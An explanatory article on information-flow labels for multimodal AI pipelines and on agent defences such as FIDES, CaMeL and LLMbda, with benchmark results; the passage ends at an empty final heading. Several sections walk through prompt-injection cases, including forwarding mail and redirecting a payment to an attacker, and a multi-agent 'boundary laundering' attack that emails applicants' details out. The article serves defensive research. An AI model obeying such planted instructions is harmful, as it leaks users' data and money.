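# Tracking sensitive content through multimodal AI pipelines with information-flow control

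## Multimodal pipelines and information-flow labels

Information-flow control is a computer-security technique that labels data with who may read it or how far to trust it. The labels follow the data as a program computes, so that restricted data cannot reach people or systems without clearance. Researchers began developing the technique in the 1970s for military files and conventional programs. In the past few years, several groups have applied it to AI agents, which are language models that call software tools on a user's behalf. Most of these groups' systems track text and tool calls, but many AI systems now also accept photographs and recordings and produce pictures, speech and runnable code. A fact can enter such a system in a photograph and leave it in a spoken sentence, and its label protects it only if the system preserves the label through that conversion.

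Several kinds of content need this protection. Personal data is the most familiar. *The Poisoned Conversation* (Braun, Grebe and colleagues, 2026), a study of leaks from chats into generated images, used disclosures of depression, pregnancy and religion. Trade secrets, such as drawings of an unreleased product, need protection for commercial reasons. Licensed material, such as a stock photograph bought for internal use, may contain nothing sensitive but still be barred from a public poster. Untrusted content need not be secret, but it must not steer what the system does. *Securing AI Agents with Information-Flow Control* (Costa, Köpf and colleagues, 2025) gives the example of an email containing instructions for the assistant to forward the top message in the mailbox to an attacker, a technique called indirect prompt injection.

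For example, a hospital assistant's context, the material the model can draw on when it generates, might contain a photo of a ward whiteboard with patients' initials and bed numbers. Only two staff members, Ada and Ben, may view the photo. The context also contains a voice memo about staffing, open to Ada, Ben and their colleague Cam, and the hospital's public style guide. Ada asks the assistant for a poster image to hang in the corridor, a spoken announcement, and a script that enters shifts into the scheduling system.

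### Where ordinary software can see the data

In a modular pipeline, a separate model handles each modality (text, images, audio) and ordinary software connects the models. A speech recogniser turns the memo into a transcript. A language model receives the transcript, Ada's request and the style guide, then writes a prompt for an image generator, a passage for a speech synthesiser and the script for a code runner. Each hand-off passes through a program that can store, block or label the data.

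Developers can still choose this design for speech. OpenAI's *Voice agents* guide recommends a chained pipeline for developers who want to inspect or alter the text between speech recognition, the agent and speech generation. The application can check the transcript against a policy before the agent responds, and hold back the audio until the workflow reaches an approved answer. The guide also describes a single model that interprets audio, decides what to do and replies in speech. That option has no separate text stage where the application could intervene.

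The hand-off to an image generator is harder to track because the prompt may not be the generator's only input. In OpenAI's image tool, the main language model rewrites the user's prompt, and software can read the rewritten version in a field named "revised_prompt". But the image model can also edit a picture already in the conversation, and by default the model chooses whether to edit a picture or create a new one. If the assistant had made its poster by editing the whiteboard photo, the prompt might have mentioned only a cheerful layout in the hospital's colours, and software that labelled the poster from the prompt alone would have missed the photo.

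Photos also often enter by a route that is hard to inspect. Many language models take images directly, using an encoder to turn the picture into vectors and another layer to adapt those vectors to the language model. An, Lu and colleagues (2026), in *Toward Native Multimodal Modeling*, call this late fusion when engineers assemble the model from separately trained parts. The image passes between these parts as a list of numbers, so a program monitoring the connection can record that the whiteboard photo went in but cannot simply read the patients' initials.

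A unified multimodal model reads and generates several modalities within one shared context. *LongCat-Next* (2026), an open model from the Chinese company Meituan, converts text, images and audio into discrete tokens, which are numbered units like the entries of a vocabulary. One network predicts the next token, whatever its modality. Separate components convert pixels and sound into tokens on input and convert tokens back on output. Ordinary software can record the photo and memo going in and the poster and announcement coming out. The model produces the outputs from the inputs in a single computation, with no prompt or transcript that they must pass through.

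Few models could yet do the hospital's whole job this way. An and colleagues class 15 models as fully symmetric, meaning that one network can both understand and generate, and their May 2026 table lists four of these as producing text, images and audio. Commercial developers are moving in the same direction. Google's *Introducing Gemini Omni* announced a model family meant to create anything from any input, starting with video and adding images and audio later, and Google DeepMind's *Gemini Omni Flash Model Card* is dated May 2026. User habits also matter because, as Braun and colleagues point out, people reuse one chat for unrelated tasks. A conversation may start with personal advice and end with a request for a picture, with the earlier disclosures still in the context.

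Alibaba's Qwen models fall between the two designs. One component, the Thinker, writes the text of a reply, and another, the Talker, turns it into speech. According to the *Qwen3-Omni Technical Report* (2025), outside software such as a safety filter can intervene on the Thinker's text before the Talker voices it. This resembles a modular hand-off, except that the Talker also receives audio and visual features from the Thinker and has access to the full conversation history. In the newer version described in the *Qwen3.5-Omni Technical Report* (2026), the Talker still receives this kind of information beyond the text, which lets it fit loudness, rhythm and emotion to the conversation. Software that approved every word of the ward announcement would therefore not have checked everything that shaped the sound. Qwen3.5-Omni can also write executable code directly from audio-visual instructions,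 so it could go from the memo to the scheduling script with no transcript in between.

Serving software, the layer that runs a model for its users, can access the intermediate data in some of these systems. The *vLLM-Omni Technical Report* (2026) describes a runtime that divides such models into stages and moves data between them, including hidden states (a network's internal vectors), codec codes (compressed units of sound) and latents (compressed representations that a decoder turns into, for example, an image). A label could travel with any of these, because attaching one does not require interpreting the data, as checking its content would.

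### Labels, the lattice and the join

Labelled data enters a system at a source, and an output leaves the system or takes effect at a sink. The hospital's sources are the photo upload, the memo recording and the style-guide file. Its sinks are the corridor wall, the loudspeaker and the scheduling system. Information-flow control assigns labels at the sources, works out a label for everything computed from the labelled data, and checks that label against a policy at each sink.

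Dorothy Denning (1976) formalized this scheme mathematically in *A Lattice Model of Secure Information Flow*. She defined information as flowing from one place to another whenever data in the first influences the value that ends up in the second. This includes both plain copying and implicit flows, in which content determines which output a program produces without appearing in that output.

Write ℓ₁ ⊑ ℓ₂ when data with label ℓ₁ may flow to a place with label ℓ₂. Denning argued that this relation must be a partial order, and the reasons are practical:

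- Data may stay where it is, so ℓ ⊑ ℓ.
- If ℓ₁ ⊑ ℓ₂ and ℓ₂ ⊑ ℓ₃, then ℓ₁ ⊑ ℓ₃. Otherwise a program could carry out a forbidden transfer in two permitted steps.
- If ℓ₁ ⊑ ℓ₂ and ℓ₂ ⊑ ℓ₁, the labels are the same, since anything under one may move to the other and a system has no use for both.

Some pairs of labels permit no flow in either direction, such as the labels on a file for Ada alone and a file for Cam alone. If those labels are ℓ₁ and ℓ₂, data computed from both files gets their join, ℓ₁ ⊔ ℓ₂, which is the least restrictive label to which both may flow. A lattice is a partial order in which every pair of elements has a join and a greatest lower bound. Costa and colleagues note that their system for agents needs only the join.

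The security rule then fits on one line. A value computed from inputs x₁, …, xₙ may reach a sink s only if

ℓ(x₁) ⊔ … ⊔ ℓ(xₙ) ⊑ ℓ(s).

Denning showed that this holds exactly when each input could have flowed to s separately. A pipeline can therefore keep a single label on each item and discard the list of inputs, because the join of their labels is enough for the check at the sink.

The effect of a join depends on what the labels record. In Denning's example, a system holds medical, financial and criminal records, and a file's label is the set of record types that went into it. Combining files takes the union of their labels, and the result may go only to places cleared for every type in that union. Sandhu's (1993) tutorial, *Lattice-Based Access Control Models*, describes the lattice behind military and government labels. When labels list permitted readers instead, the join is the intersection,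 because only people on every list may read the result. In Costa and colleagues' example, if A, B and C may read one document and B, C and D may read another, then only B and C may read a text that combines them. Shorter lists are more restrictive, so the bottom of this lattice is "everyone", the label for public data, and the top is the empty list.

These labels concern confidentiality, or who may learn something. Integrity labels record how far a system may trust data. The simplest version has two values, trusted and untrusted, and anything computed partly from untrusted data is untrusted. A finer version lists everyone who could have written to the data. Its join is a union, because each input brings its own possible authors. Costa and colleagues pair the two kinds, so one label might be "untrusted; readers Ada and Ben".

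Their system, which handles text and tool calls, checks such pairs just before a tool runs. A message may go out through a channel only if everyone who can read the channel is on the message's list of readers, a policy that *Optimizing Agent Planning for Security and Autonomy* (2026) calls permitted flow. A tool call with real consequences may proceed only if the call and its arguments are trusted. The hospital's scheduling script falls under the second policy. Suppose the photo of the ward whiteboard is untrusted, because visitors can write on the board, while the memo and the style guide are trusted. A script derived from the photo is then also untrusted, so the assistant may not run it on its own authority, even if only Ada and Ben will ever see the schedule.

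### Access control, content filtering and taint tracking

Hospitals already restrict who can open files, which would stop Cam from opening the whiteboard photo. But it would not stop Ada, who is allowed to open the photo, from giving it to an assistant that makes a poster from it. The poster is a new file with its own permissions. Denning criticised the access controls of the time because they governed immediate access to an object but not where the information went next.

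Some systems of the 1970s closed the gap with a coarse rule. They gave each running process a clearance. The process could read only data that could flow to that clearance, and could write only to places to which that clearance could flow. In the hospital example, an assistant cleared for material that Ada and Ben may read could open all three items, but could write only where nobody except Ada and Ben would look. This is secure, but it prevents the assistant from producing a public poster.

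A content filter instead examines a finished output for forbidden content, such as a patient's name. Costa and colleagues class input and output filters as probabilistic defences, which may catch an attack but cannot guarantee it. Filtering is harder outside text. A filter for posters, for example, would have to spot initials in small type in the background of a picture.

Taint tracking labels data from chosen sources and passes the label to anything the system computes from that data. If a pipeline uses labelled patient records to make a poster, the poster gets the same label, whatever it shows. This works without detecting a patient's initials in the image, but it also means that harmless posters made from those records are labelled.

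### The hospital outputs under conservative merge

To compute an output's label, the software has to know which inputs went into that output. This can be traced line by line in a conventional program but not in a language model, so the usual approach is conservative merge, which gives the model's output the join of the labels of everything in its context. Costa and colleagues adopt this rule because they have no precise way to propagate labels through a language model, and they acknowledge that it may be too strict.

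For the hospital assistant the calculation is short. Ada's request adds no restriction, since Costa and colleagues treat a user's message as public by default. The join of the three items is

{Ada, Ben} ∩ {Ada, Ben, Cam} ∩ everyone = {Ada, Ben}.

Every output of the session receives that label, whatever its modality. But suppose the assistant based the poster's design only on the style guide, the announcement on the memo, and the script on both the photo and the memo.

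| Output | Items it used | Readers, judged by those items | Readers under conservative merge |
|---|---|---|---|
| Poster image | Style guide | Everyone | Ada, Ben |
| Spoken announcement | Voice memo | Ada, Ben, Cam | Ada, Ben |
| Scheduling script | Photo, voice memo | Ada, Ben | Ada, Ben |

Only the script ends up with the right list. Cam is not allowed to hear the announcement, even though it is drawn entirely from a memo that Cam is allowed to play. The error is worst for the poster, which contains only public material but which the software must keep off the corridor wall. Safely relaxing the poster's label would require evidence that a different whiteboard photo would have produced the same poster, a requirement related to the formal guarantee of noninterference.

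Newer systems behave in much the same way. *Flowsh* (2026) is a command shell for AI agents, so it is relevant to the code runner but not to pictures or sound. It adds the label of each input to a command to the labels of that command's outputs, even if the input made no difference. *GIF* (2026), a proposal for measuring flows inside language models, notes that existing agent systems mostly track flow around the model and that conservative labels can over-restrict later steps. A modular pipeline can avoid some of this over-restriction by making the poster in a fresh call that receives only the style guide, but someone must decide before the model starts work that the poster needs nothing else. The image prompt must also come from a model that has not seen the photo, because otherwise the prompt carries the label {Ada, Ben}.

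Label creep is the spread of restrictive labels to data that does not depend on the restricted content. *Agent Security is a Systems Problem* (2026) calls its end state "label explosion", where every piece of data carries every label and tracking loses its purpose. Stored files make label creep worse because a careful system has to preserve their labels. *Flowsh*, for example, keeps the label on a file after the command finishes and adds it to any later command that reads the file. If the hospital saves the poster as a template, and next week's session also includes a note that only Cam may read, the two lists of permitted readers have no name in common, so nobody may look at the new poster.

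## What counts as a leak

Under conservative merge, the hospital's poster got a label that kept it off the corridor wall, even though the whiteboard photo had made no difference to the poster. Relaxing such a label safely requires a definition of "made no difference". Several definitions are in use, and they lead to different conclusions about the following poster.

Suppose the hospital assistant's context contains the public style guide and one patient's secret diagnosis. The patient has asthma, bronchitis, eczema or psoriasis, and the four are equally likely to anyone who has not seen the diagnosis. Ada asks for a waiting-room poster about hand-washing. The model uses a blue palette if the patient has a lung disease (asthma or bronchitis) and a green one if the patient has a skin disease (eczema or psoriasis). Nothing else on the poster depends on the patient.

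### Noninterference

The classic definition comes from Goguen and Meseguer (1982), in *Security Policies and Security Models*. They considered a computer shared by users with high and low clearances. Noninterference requires that deleting every command from the high users would change nothing that the low users observe. Clarkson and Schneider (2009), in *Hyperproperties*, write this as a condition on T, the set of all runs that a deterministic system can perform:

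for every run t in T, there is a run t′ in T such that t′ has no secret inputs and the public events of t′ are the same as those of t.

For a program that receives its data at the start, it is more convenient to change the secret than to delete it. Schoepe, Balliu and colleagues, in *Explicit Secrecy*, use a version in which any two starting memories that agree on public data must lead to the same visible output. For a model call, let M(s, p) be the output for secret s and public material p. Noninterference then means

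M(s, p) = M(s′, p) for all s, s′ and p.

The poster fails, because M(asthma, style guide) is blue and M(eczema, style guide) is green.

A monitor cannot discover this by watching the assistant make one poster, because a blue poster for an asthma patient looks the same whether the assistant uses blue for everyone or only for lung patients. Clarkson and Schneider call noninterference a hyperproperty, a condition on the whole set of runs, because whether one run is acceptable depends on which other runs are possible. They contrast it with rules such as "do not write to the network after reading a file", where each run can be judged on its own.

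One way to check such a condition is self-composition, which *Verifying Hyperproperties with TLA* (Lamport and Schneider, 2021) uses to turn a comparison between runs into an ordinary property of a derived system. For noninterference, the derived system can be two copies of the original with the same public inputs and different secrets. A tester can imitate this by generating a poster for each diagnosis. If the model is deterministic, any difference between the posters proves a violation. Four identical posters would be only weak evidence of noninterference, because the definition covers every secret and every public context.

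### Random outputs and runs that never finish

Generative models usually sample their outputs, so the same context can produce different posters. This rules out observational determinism, a related condition that requires a system to look deterministic to a public observer. A sampling model would fail this condition even if the context contained no secret.

A rule that only requires the same outputs to be possible for every value of a secret is too weak. Clarkson and Schneider describe a system that outputs 0, 1 or the value of a secret bit. Both outputs are possible whatever the bit is, but if the system picks among its three options with equal probability, the output matches the bit two times in three.

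Probabilistic noninterference closes this gap by comparing probabilities. For every possible output y, it requires

P(y | s, p) = P(y | s′, p) for all s, s′ and p.

A language model that depends even slightly on every token in its context cannot meet this condition. In a transformer, attention moves information between tokens. Xu, Li and colleagues (2026) note in *Sightline*, a study of data flow through language-model calls, that attention reads every input in a prompt at least a little. An input can be read without affecting the output, but to satisfy the equation, all the small effects of replacing "asthma" with "eczema" would have to cancel exactly, for every output and every context. If the replacement moves the probability of a blue poster from 0.500 to 0.501, the model fails. Always choosing the most likely token would hide most such shifts, but not where two tokens are almost tied.

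A secret can also influence whether a run finishes. Termination-insensitive noninterference ignores this influence by comparing only runs that do finish. This makes the condition easier to enforce, but Askarov, Hunt and colleagues showed in *Termination-Insensitive Noninterference Leaks More Than Just a Bit* that it can leak a lot of information. For example, a program could number the four diagnoses, count upwards on a public screen, and hang when it reached the patient's number. No run finishes, so the program satisfies the condition, yet anyone watching the screen learns the diagnosis.

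Garby, Gordon and Sands (2026), in *AI Agents, Conversations, and Information Flow*, needed a definition for agents that are both random and liable to hang. They treat the probability of never finishing as missing from the output distribution, so the remaining probabilities may sum to less than 1. Two such distributions μ and ν are compatible if some third distribution ω, also with a total of at most 1, satisfies

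μ(y) ≤ ω(y) and ν(y) ≤ ω(y) for every output y.

Termination-insensitive probabilistic noninterference requires that changing the secret always gives a compatible distribution of public outputs. Informally, two distributions are compatible when they could become equal if the program finished more often with each secret.

Suppose the assistant makes a blue poster with probability 0.9 for asthma and 0.7 for eczema, and otherwise hangs. These distributions are compatible, since ω can give blue a probability of 0.9. If it made a blue poster for asthma and a green one for eczema, each with probability 0.9, ω would need a total probability of 1.8, which is more than the maximum of 1, so the assistant would fail the definition. Garby and colleagues also prove that the statistical distance between compatible distributions is at most the average of their probabilities of not finishing. In the first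 example, the distance is 0.1 and the limit is 0.2. For a system that always finishes, the limit is zero and the definition becomes ordinary probabilistic noninterference.

### Explicit secrecy

Many practical taint trackers follow copying and calculation but ignore implicit flows. Schoepe and colleagues devised explicit secrecy to state what such tools guarantee. Take the path that one run followed through a program, and let g be the combined effect of that path's operations on the data. Explicit secrecy requires that

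if d₁ and d₂ agree on public data, then g(d₁) and g(d₂) agree on public data.

The secret may still determine which path the program takes. Schoepe and colleagues give the example of a program that sets a public variable to 1 if a secret is 0 and to 2 otherwise, then prints the variable. The printed number reveals whether the secret is 0, but the program passes because each path only stores a constant and prints it.

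A program can satisfy noninterference and still violate explicit secrecy, so explicit secrecy is not simply a weaker form of noninterference. For example, a program that prints the diagnosis if it is asthma, and otherwise prints the word "asthma", satisfies noninterference because its output is always the same. It violates explicit secrecy because one of its paths prints the secret variable.

Whether the poster passes depends on where the palette is chosen. If ordinary software looks up the diagnosis, selects blue or green and passes the colour to an image generator that receives no other secret, each path contains only a constant colour and the program passes. If one model reads the diagnosis and draws the poster in a single step, the software has no visible branch to exempt. When that step is treated as an operation on data, it must produce the same poster for every diagnosis, as under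 noninterference, and it fails. Schoepe and colleagues let the designer decide which parts of a system count as data and which as control, so two developers could get different verdicts on the same pair of posters.

### Measuring a leak in bits

Quantitative information flow measures how much an output reveals. The usual measure is the mutual information between the secret S and the output Y:

I(S; Y) = H(S) − H(S | Y).

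Here H(S) is an observer's uncertainty about the secret before seeing the output, and H(S | Y) is the average uncertainty afterwards, both in bits. Four equally likely diagnoses give H(S) = log₂ 4 = 2 bits. A blue poster narrows the diagnosis to asthma or bronchitis, and a green one narrows it to eczema or psoriasis. Either way, two equally likely possibilities remain, so H(S | Y) = log₂ 2 = 1 bit. The palette therefore leaks 1 of the 2 bits, while a poster that printed the diagnosis would leak both.

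With the public material fixed, the leak is zero exactly when every diagnosis gives the same distribution of posters. This condition is probabilistic noninterference for that context. The measure is more useful when the leak is small but not zero. For example, a model that makes blue posters with probability 0.500 for lung patients and 0.501 for skin patients leaks less than a millionth of a bit through the colour.

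An average can hide a serious leak, however. If the assistant used red only for psoriasis and blue for the other three diagnoses, the palette would leak about 0.81 bits, less than the original design, but a red poster would completely reveal a psoriasis patient's diagnosis. A limit on each image also does not limit what someone learns by requesting several. If the model followed the original design but picked the intended palette only 90% of the time, independently for each poster, one poster would leak about 0.53 bits and two would leak about 0.74.

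Restricting a model's output is a simple way to cap a leak. If the model can return only one of n values, it reveals at most log₂ n bits. Costa and colleagues apply the same reasoning to integrity in FIDES, their agent system, where a policy may accept a yes-or-no answer derived from untrusted text because the text can influence only 1 bit. The cap is of little use for a free-form picture, since an uncompressed image of 1,024 by 1,024 pixels at 24 bits per pixel can hold about 25 million bits. A developer could instead let the model choose between two palettes and have ordinary software draw a poster from a public template, which would cap the leak at 1 bit per poster.

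### Reach

Reach applies to one recorded output, so unlike noninterference it does not require comparing runs. In Xu and colleagues' definition, an input reaches an output if the output visibly reflects the input's content. The output might copy, translate or summarise that content. The influence can also be less direct, as when the content determines which option the model picks, what number it calculates, or the output's layout or length. An input that the model ignored does not reach the output.

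The diagnosis reaches the poster under this definition because it determined the palette. Earlier work on reach used language models as reviewers, giving them the prompt, the input and the output. But a reviewer who saw one blue hand-washing poster would have little reason to connect the colour with asthma. Xu and colleagues studied text outputs, where a copied name or a yes-or-no decision is usually easier to trace.

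Reach also differs from sensitivity to small changes in an input. A model may be so certain to choose blue for asthma that slightly altering its internal representation of "asthma" has almost no effect. The diagnosis still determined the palette, so Xu and colleagues argue that the palette should carry the diagnosis's label.

Refusals are harder to classify. Xu and colleagues list them among the cases where an input may have no observable use and so not reach the output. But if the assistant refused to make posters only for psoriasis patients, the refusal would reveal the diagnosis. A reviewer can also see a leak where there is none. If a model wrote "asthma" on every poster, the word would look copied from an asthma patient's record, even though the record made no difference.

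Xu and colleagues examined program calls from 2,103 families of open-source repositories and found that 12–14% of inputs did not reach the output. Conservative merge would add the labels of those inputs to the output too, but it never misses an input that does reach the output.

The definitions would guarantee the following for a poster generated with the diagnosis in context. The definitions are listed roughly from strict to lenient, although explicit secrecy and noninterference can each reject programs that the other accepts.

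| Guarantee | Meaning for the generated poster |
|---|---|
| Noninterference | Changing the diagnosis would not alter a single pixel. |
| Probabilistic noninterference | Changing the diagnosis would not alter the probability of any poster. |
| Termination-insensitive probabilistic noninterference | The diagnosis may affect whether a poster appears, and the probabilities may differ only as far as that allows. |
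| Explicit secrecy | No data operation on the path taken carried the diagnosis into the poster, but the diagnosis may have selected the path. |
| Mutual information of at most k bits | On average, the poster reduces uncertainty about the diagnosis by no more than k bits. |
| No reach | This poster shows no visible use of the diagnosis, but another diagnosis might have produced a different poster. |

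### A theorem for the program around the model

A program can satisfy noninterference even if the model inside it does not. One way is conservative merge, which labels the poster secret if the context contains the diagnosis, so a public observer never sees the poster. Noninterference restricts only what the observer can see, so the model may use the diagnosis in any way.

Garby and colleagues built a small programming language for agents, LLMbda, on this principle. Every value and every conversation with a model has a label. Sending a message joins its label to the conversation's. The program evaluates the model's reply under the conversation's label, so everything computed from the reply carries at least that label, even if the reply is code. A program can also empty a conversation or make a temporary copy of it. The hospital's program could start with an empty conversation, send only the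 style guide, and receive a poster with a public label, as long as no secret had influenced the decision to do so.

The main theorem is that every LLMbda program satisfies termination-insensitive probabilistic noninterference for observers at every level. The proof compares a program with a modified version that skips any computation once its label hides it from the observer, and substitutes a dummy value. The modified version never processes the secret, so it behaves the same whatever the secret is. It also produces each visible output at least as often as the original program. Its distribution can therefore serve as the ω in the definition of compatibility for any pair of secrets.

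A second theorem shows that endorsement, the deliberate relabelling of untrusted data as trusted, cannot cause a confidentiality leak, even if an attacker chooses all the untrusted data. A third shows that the interpreter for LLMbda programs matches the mathematical definition of the language. The proof checker Lean has verified all three.

The theorems assume almost nothing about the model's quality, but the third assumes that each reply is an independent draw whose probabilities depend only on the conversation so far. A hosted model that retained information from other conversations would break this assumption. Garby and colleagues also treat all data sources as part of the program, and they rely on its developer to label those sources correctly and place checks at the sinks. If someone labelled the diagnosis public, the poster could reveal it even though every theorem would still hold.

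The model in these theorems exchanges text strings with the program, and its replies can include code. An image encoded as a string would fit this interface, but Garby and colleagues demonstrated the language only on text and code.

FIDES has a narrower guarantee. Costa and colleagues chose explicit secrecy for a particular agent loop and assumed a deterministic model. They acknowledge that an adversary who sees the sequence of tool calls may learn something from the agent's decisions. Their formal model treats the conversation, including the model's replies, as control, and only the tools' stored data as data. Since explicit secrecy holds control fixed, the definition alone would not rule out a model copying the diagnosis into an image prompt. FIDES can stop this with the label check before the tool runs.

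Costa and colleagues considered noninterference too restrictive for agents because they thought it would essentially forbid calls to tools that may write public data after any call that may have read a secret. LLMbda's separate conversations can avoid this, because reading a secret in one conversation need not restrict another.

A guarantee also depends on the labels covering the whole program. Garby and colleagues found a gap in CaMeL, an agent system in which one model writes code from the user's request and a quarantined model without tools reads untrusted data. CaMeL tracks labels inside its interpreter, but an ordinary retry loop outside the interpreter carries no labels. Whether the policy blocked an attempt can depend on a secret, so each attempt can reveal one bit, and an attacker who can trigger enough retries can recover the whole secret. LLMbda programs run their retry loops inside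 the labelled language.

### Results on a banking benchmark

Garby and colleagues wrote an agent, Randori, in the language to test whether it is usable despite being so strict. Randori first practises in an artificial world with trusted data, so that error messages from failed attempts do not taint the code it finally runs. The researchers tested it on the banking tasks of AgentDojo, a benchmark of prompt-injection attacks on agents that use tools. They ran every combination of the 16 user tasks and 9 attacks three times with each of three models, and the agent resisted the attack in all but two of the 1,296 runs.

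Both failures involved the same task, in which the user asks the agent to pay a bill described in a text file. The attacker replaces the file's contents with a different payment request. The label check blocks any payment that uses details from the file unless Randori's code endorses them. The code endorses them because it could not otherwise pay any such bill, and the money goes to the attacker.

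The total overstates how thoroughly the label checks were tested. In 97 of the 144 combinations of task and attack, the attack needs an action that would never appear in the code for the user's task. Writing the code before reading untrusted data defeats these attacks without labels. The other 47 combinations account for 423 runs, including both failures. Even with CaMeL's policy checks off, the attack succeeded in only 5 of the 622 attacked runs that finished.

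The systems differed more in how many tasks they completed without an attack:

| Agent | GPT-5.2 | MiMo-v2.5 |
|---|---|---|
| Randori, label checks on | 36 of 48 | 31 of 48 |
| CaMeL, policy checks off | 32 of 48 | 34 of 48 |
| CaMeL, policy checks on | 18 of 48 | 18 of 48 |

Randori performed about as well as CaMeL did without policy checks, and completed roughly twice as many tasks as CaMeL did with them. With only 16 distinct tasks, the confidence intervals extend about 19 to 27 percentage points either way, and even those of Randori and the policy-checked CaMeL overlap. Randori also implements only a subset of CaMeL's policies. Some of its advantage comes from endorsement, since its score on MiMo-v2.5 fell from 31 to 26 when endorsement was disabled.

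These results show that an agent can do useful work under LLMbda's rules, but they only partly answer Costa and colleagues' objection, which was about confidentiality. The benchmark measures whether injected text makes an agent carry out an attacker's goal, such as sending money, not how much a text reply or generated image reveals about a secret in the context.

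## Tracking labels between model calls

LLMbda and FIDES both treat the model as a black box. The surrounding software can observe each call's inputs and output, but not which input influenced which part of the output. It does control what goes into each call, and several agent systems use this to keep restricted or untrusted data out of most calls, so conservative merge has fewer labels to combine.

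### How FIDES handles a request

FIDES runs a loop around a language model called the planner. The planner reads the conversation so far and either answers the user or requests a tool call. Ordinary software runs the tool, adds the result to the conversation and queries the planner again. In one of Costa and colleagues' examples, a user asks the assistant to summarise the top three emails in a mailbox and send the summary to someone on Slack.

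Labelling starts with tool results. The mail tool returns a structured record, and a label can cover the whole record or a single field. The body of an email is untrusted because an attacker could have written it, while a timestamp generated by the mail system might be trusted.

The software also keeps a context label, which is the join of the labels of every message in the conversation. Each tool call the planner requests gets this label, since any of the messages could have prompted it. In a basic agent, the email bodies would enter the conversation and make it untrusted. The agent then couldn't take any action that requires trust for the rest of the conversation, even one unrelated to the emails.

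FIDES avoids this by hiding data in variables. If a field's label satisfies ℓ(field) ⊑ ℓ(context), adding the field would leave the context label unchanged, so the software adds it to the planner's context. Otherwise, the software stores the field in memory and gives the planner only a variable name. The planner can pass that name to a tool, and the software substitutes the content, with its own label, just before the tool runs. A single call can therefore combine a trusted recipient with an untrusted message.

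The planner cannot summarise text it cannot read, so it sends the variables and an instruction to a quarantined model, which has no tools. The software stores the answer in a new variable, labelled with the join of the context label and the labels of all the variables in the query. A malicious email can still corrupt the summary, but it cannot make the planner call a tool. If the planner needs information about the emails, it can request a yes-or-no answer and read only that.

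Before each tool call, the software compares the labels of the call and its arguments with the tool's policy. In the example, the user chose both the action and the recipient, so both are trusted. The policy can allow the message to be untrusted. A policy based on readers would also require the recipient to be on the reader lists of all three emails. If a call fails the check, the software blocks it and notifies the planner, which can then try another route.

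### FIDES on AgentDojo

Costa and colleagues tested FIDES on the 97 user tasks of AgentDojo, which use text and tool calls and cover an office workspace, travel booking, banking and Slack. They labelled a field as untrusted if any of the benchmark's attacks targeted it. With GPT-4o and no policy checks, 152 attacks succeeded against a basic agent and 21 against FIDES, after they removed cases that the benchmark had scored incorrectly. With the checks on, no attack succeeded against either agent.

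The checks alone were therefore enough to stop the attacks. Hiding data in variables mattered because it let the agent finish more tasks while the checks were on. The table gives the percentage of tasks that GPT-4o completed when there was no attack:

| Environment | Basic agent, checks off | Basic agent, checks on | FIDES, checks on |
|---|---|---|---|
| Workspace | 75.0 | 37.0 | 59.0 |
| Travel | 70.0 | 73.0 | 41.0 |
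| Banking | 98.8 | 37.5 | 52.5 |
| Slack | 93.3 | 20.0 | 47.6 |

On average, FIDES completed about 8 percentage points more tasks than the basic agent with checks. With OpenAI's o1 reasoning model, the advantage was 16 points. Travel was the exception with GPT-4o. The policies let many travel tools run in untrusted contexts, so the checks didn't lower the basic agent's score, while FIDES's planner often mishandled its variables. Switching to o1 raised FIDES's travel score from 41% to 68%.

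The experiment tested integrity more thoroughly than confidentiality. FIDES can hide a field because it is untrusted or because it is confidential, but in these runs it hid only untrusted fields and did not use restricted answer types. The results show that a planner can work without seeing untrusted text, but they are weaker evidence about whether it could work without seeing secrets, as the hospital assistant would have to.

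*Optimizing Agent Planning for Security and Autonomy* measured how many AgentDojo tasks an agent could finish without asking a person for approval. With OpenAI's o3-mini, an agent that needed approval for every consequential action finished 24.3% of tasks unaided. Adding labels and conservative merge, without hiding anything, raised this to 35.5%. FIDES reached 50.1%, and Prudentia, a new agent built on FIDES, reached 59.1%. Prudentia tells its planner the labels and policies in advance and requires it to justify revealing a variable before doing so.

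The models in these tests date from 2024 and 2025. A stronger planner should make fewer mistakes with variables, as o1 did, but it cannot complete a task whose only solution breaks the policy.

### CaMeL and plans written in advance

CaMeL, from Google DeepMind, isolates its planner more strictly. Nikolaou, Eckhoff and colleagues (2026) describe the design in *CaMeLoT*, a proposal for checking CaMeL's plans before they run. The model that reads the user's request writes the whole plan in advance, in a restricted form of Python. An interpreter then runs the plan, storing tool results in variables and calling the quarantined model like an ordinary function.

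The interpreter tags each value with its sources and who may read it. Before a tool runs, a policy function checks these tags and allows or denies the call. Suppose the user asks for meeting notes to be summarized and the summary sent to a particular employee. An instruction hidden in the notes could distort the summary or affect which of the program's existing branches runs, but it could not add a new step that sends the notes to an attacker.

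The tags are necessary even though the plan is fixed. *On the Relative Security of Prompt Injection* (2026) gives an example in which an injected instruction makes the quarantined model quote private notes in an email reply. The plan already included sending a reply, so the attacker does not need to add a tool call. CaMeL-style tags mark the reply as private because one of the quarantined model's inputs was private, so the software can refuse to send it.

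CaMeL and FIDES differ in when the planner chooses its actions. FIDES's planner chooses each action after the previous tool has run, and it can reveal a variable, which makes the context label more restrictive. CaMeL's planner must finish writing the program before any tool runs. *Kaer* (2026) points out that a plan fixed in advance has to account for every possible course of events. That is practical for "summarise these notes and send them", but not for "do whatever is on my to-do list".

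*CaMeLs Can Use Computers Too* (2026) extends the approach beyond text to agents that operate a computer through screenshots. A quarantined vision model answers the questions in the plan about what is on the screen.

### Labels lost between agents

Protecting each agent separately does not protect a system made of several. In *Can CaMeLs Talk?*, Peters-Gill, Semler and colleagues (2026) connected three CaMeL agents, all running on GPT-5.2: an orchestrator, a database agent and a notification agent. The user asked the system to send Julie a summary of job applicants' details on Slack. The researchers had planted in the database an instruction to email the details to an outside address.

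The database agent and the orchestrator kept the planted text in variables and followed their original plans. The orchestrator then pasted the summary into the instruction it sent to the notification agent. That agent treated the whole instruction as a trusted request from its user, so its planner read the attacker's text and wrote a program with an extra step that emailed the applicants' details to the attacker. Peters-Gill and colleagues call this boundary laundering.

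Their solution, multi-CaMeL, sends instructions and data through separate channels. The receiving agent's planner gets only the trusted instruction, while the data stays in variables with its labels. On their text benchmark, attacks succeeded 12.9% of the time without CaMeL, 0.2% with individually protected agents and 0.0% with multi-CaMeL. Laundering was therefore rare among the benchmark's attacks, but an attacker who knew how the agents were connected could attempt it deliberately.

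A modular pipeline has a similar boundary wherever one model's output becomes another model's prompt. If the hospital's software passed the transcript of Cam's voice memo to the language model as though Ada had typed it, words spoken in the recording would become trusted instructions. The transcript would also lose its reader list, so its contents could end up on a public poster.

### Microsoft's prototypes

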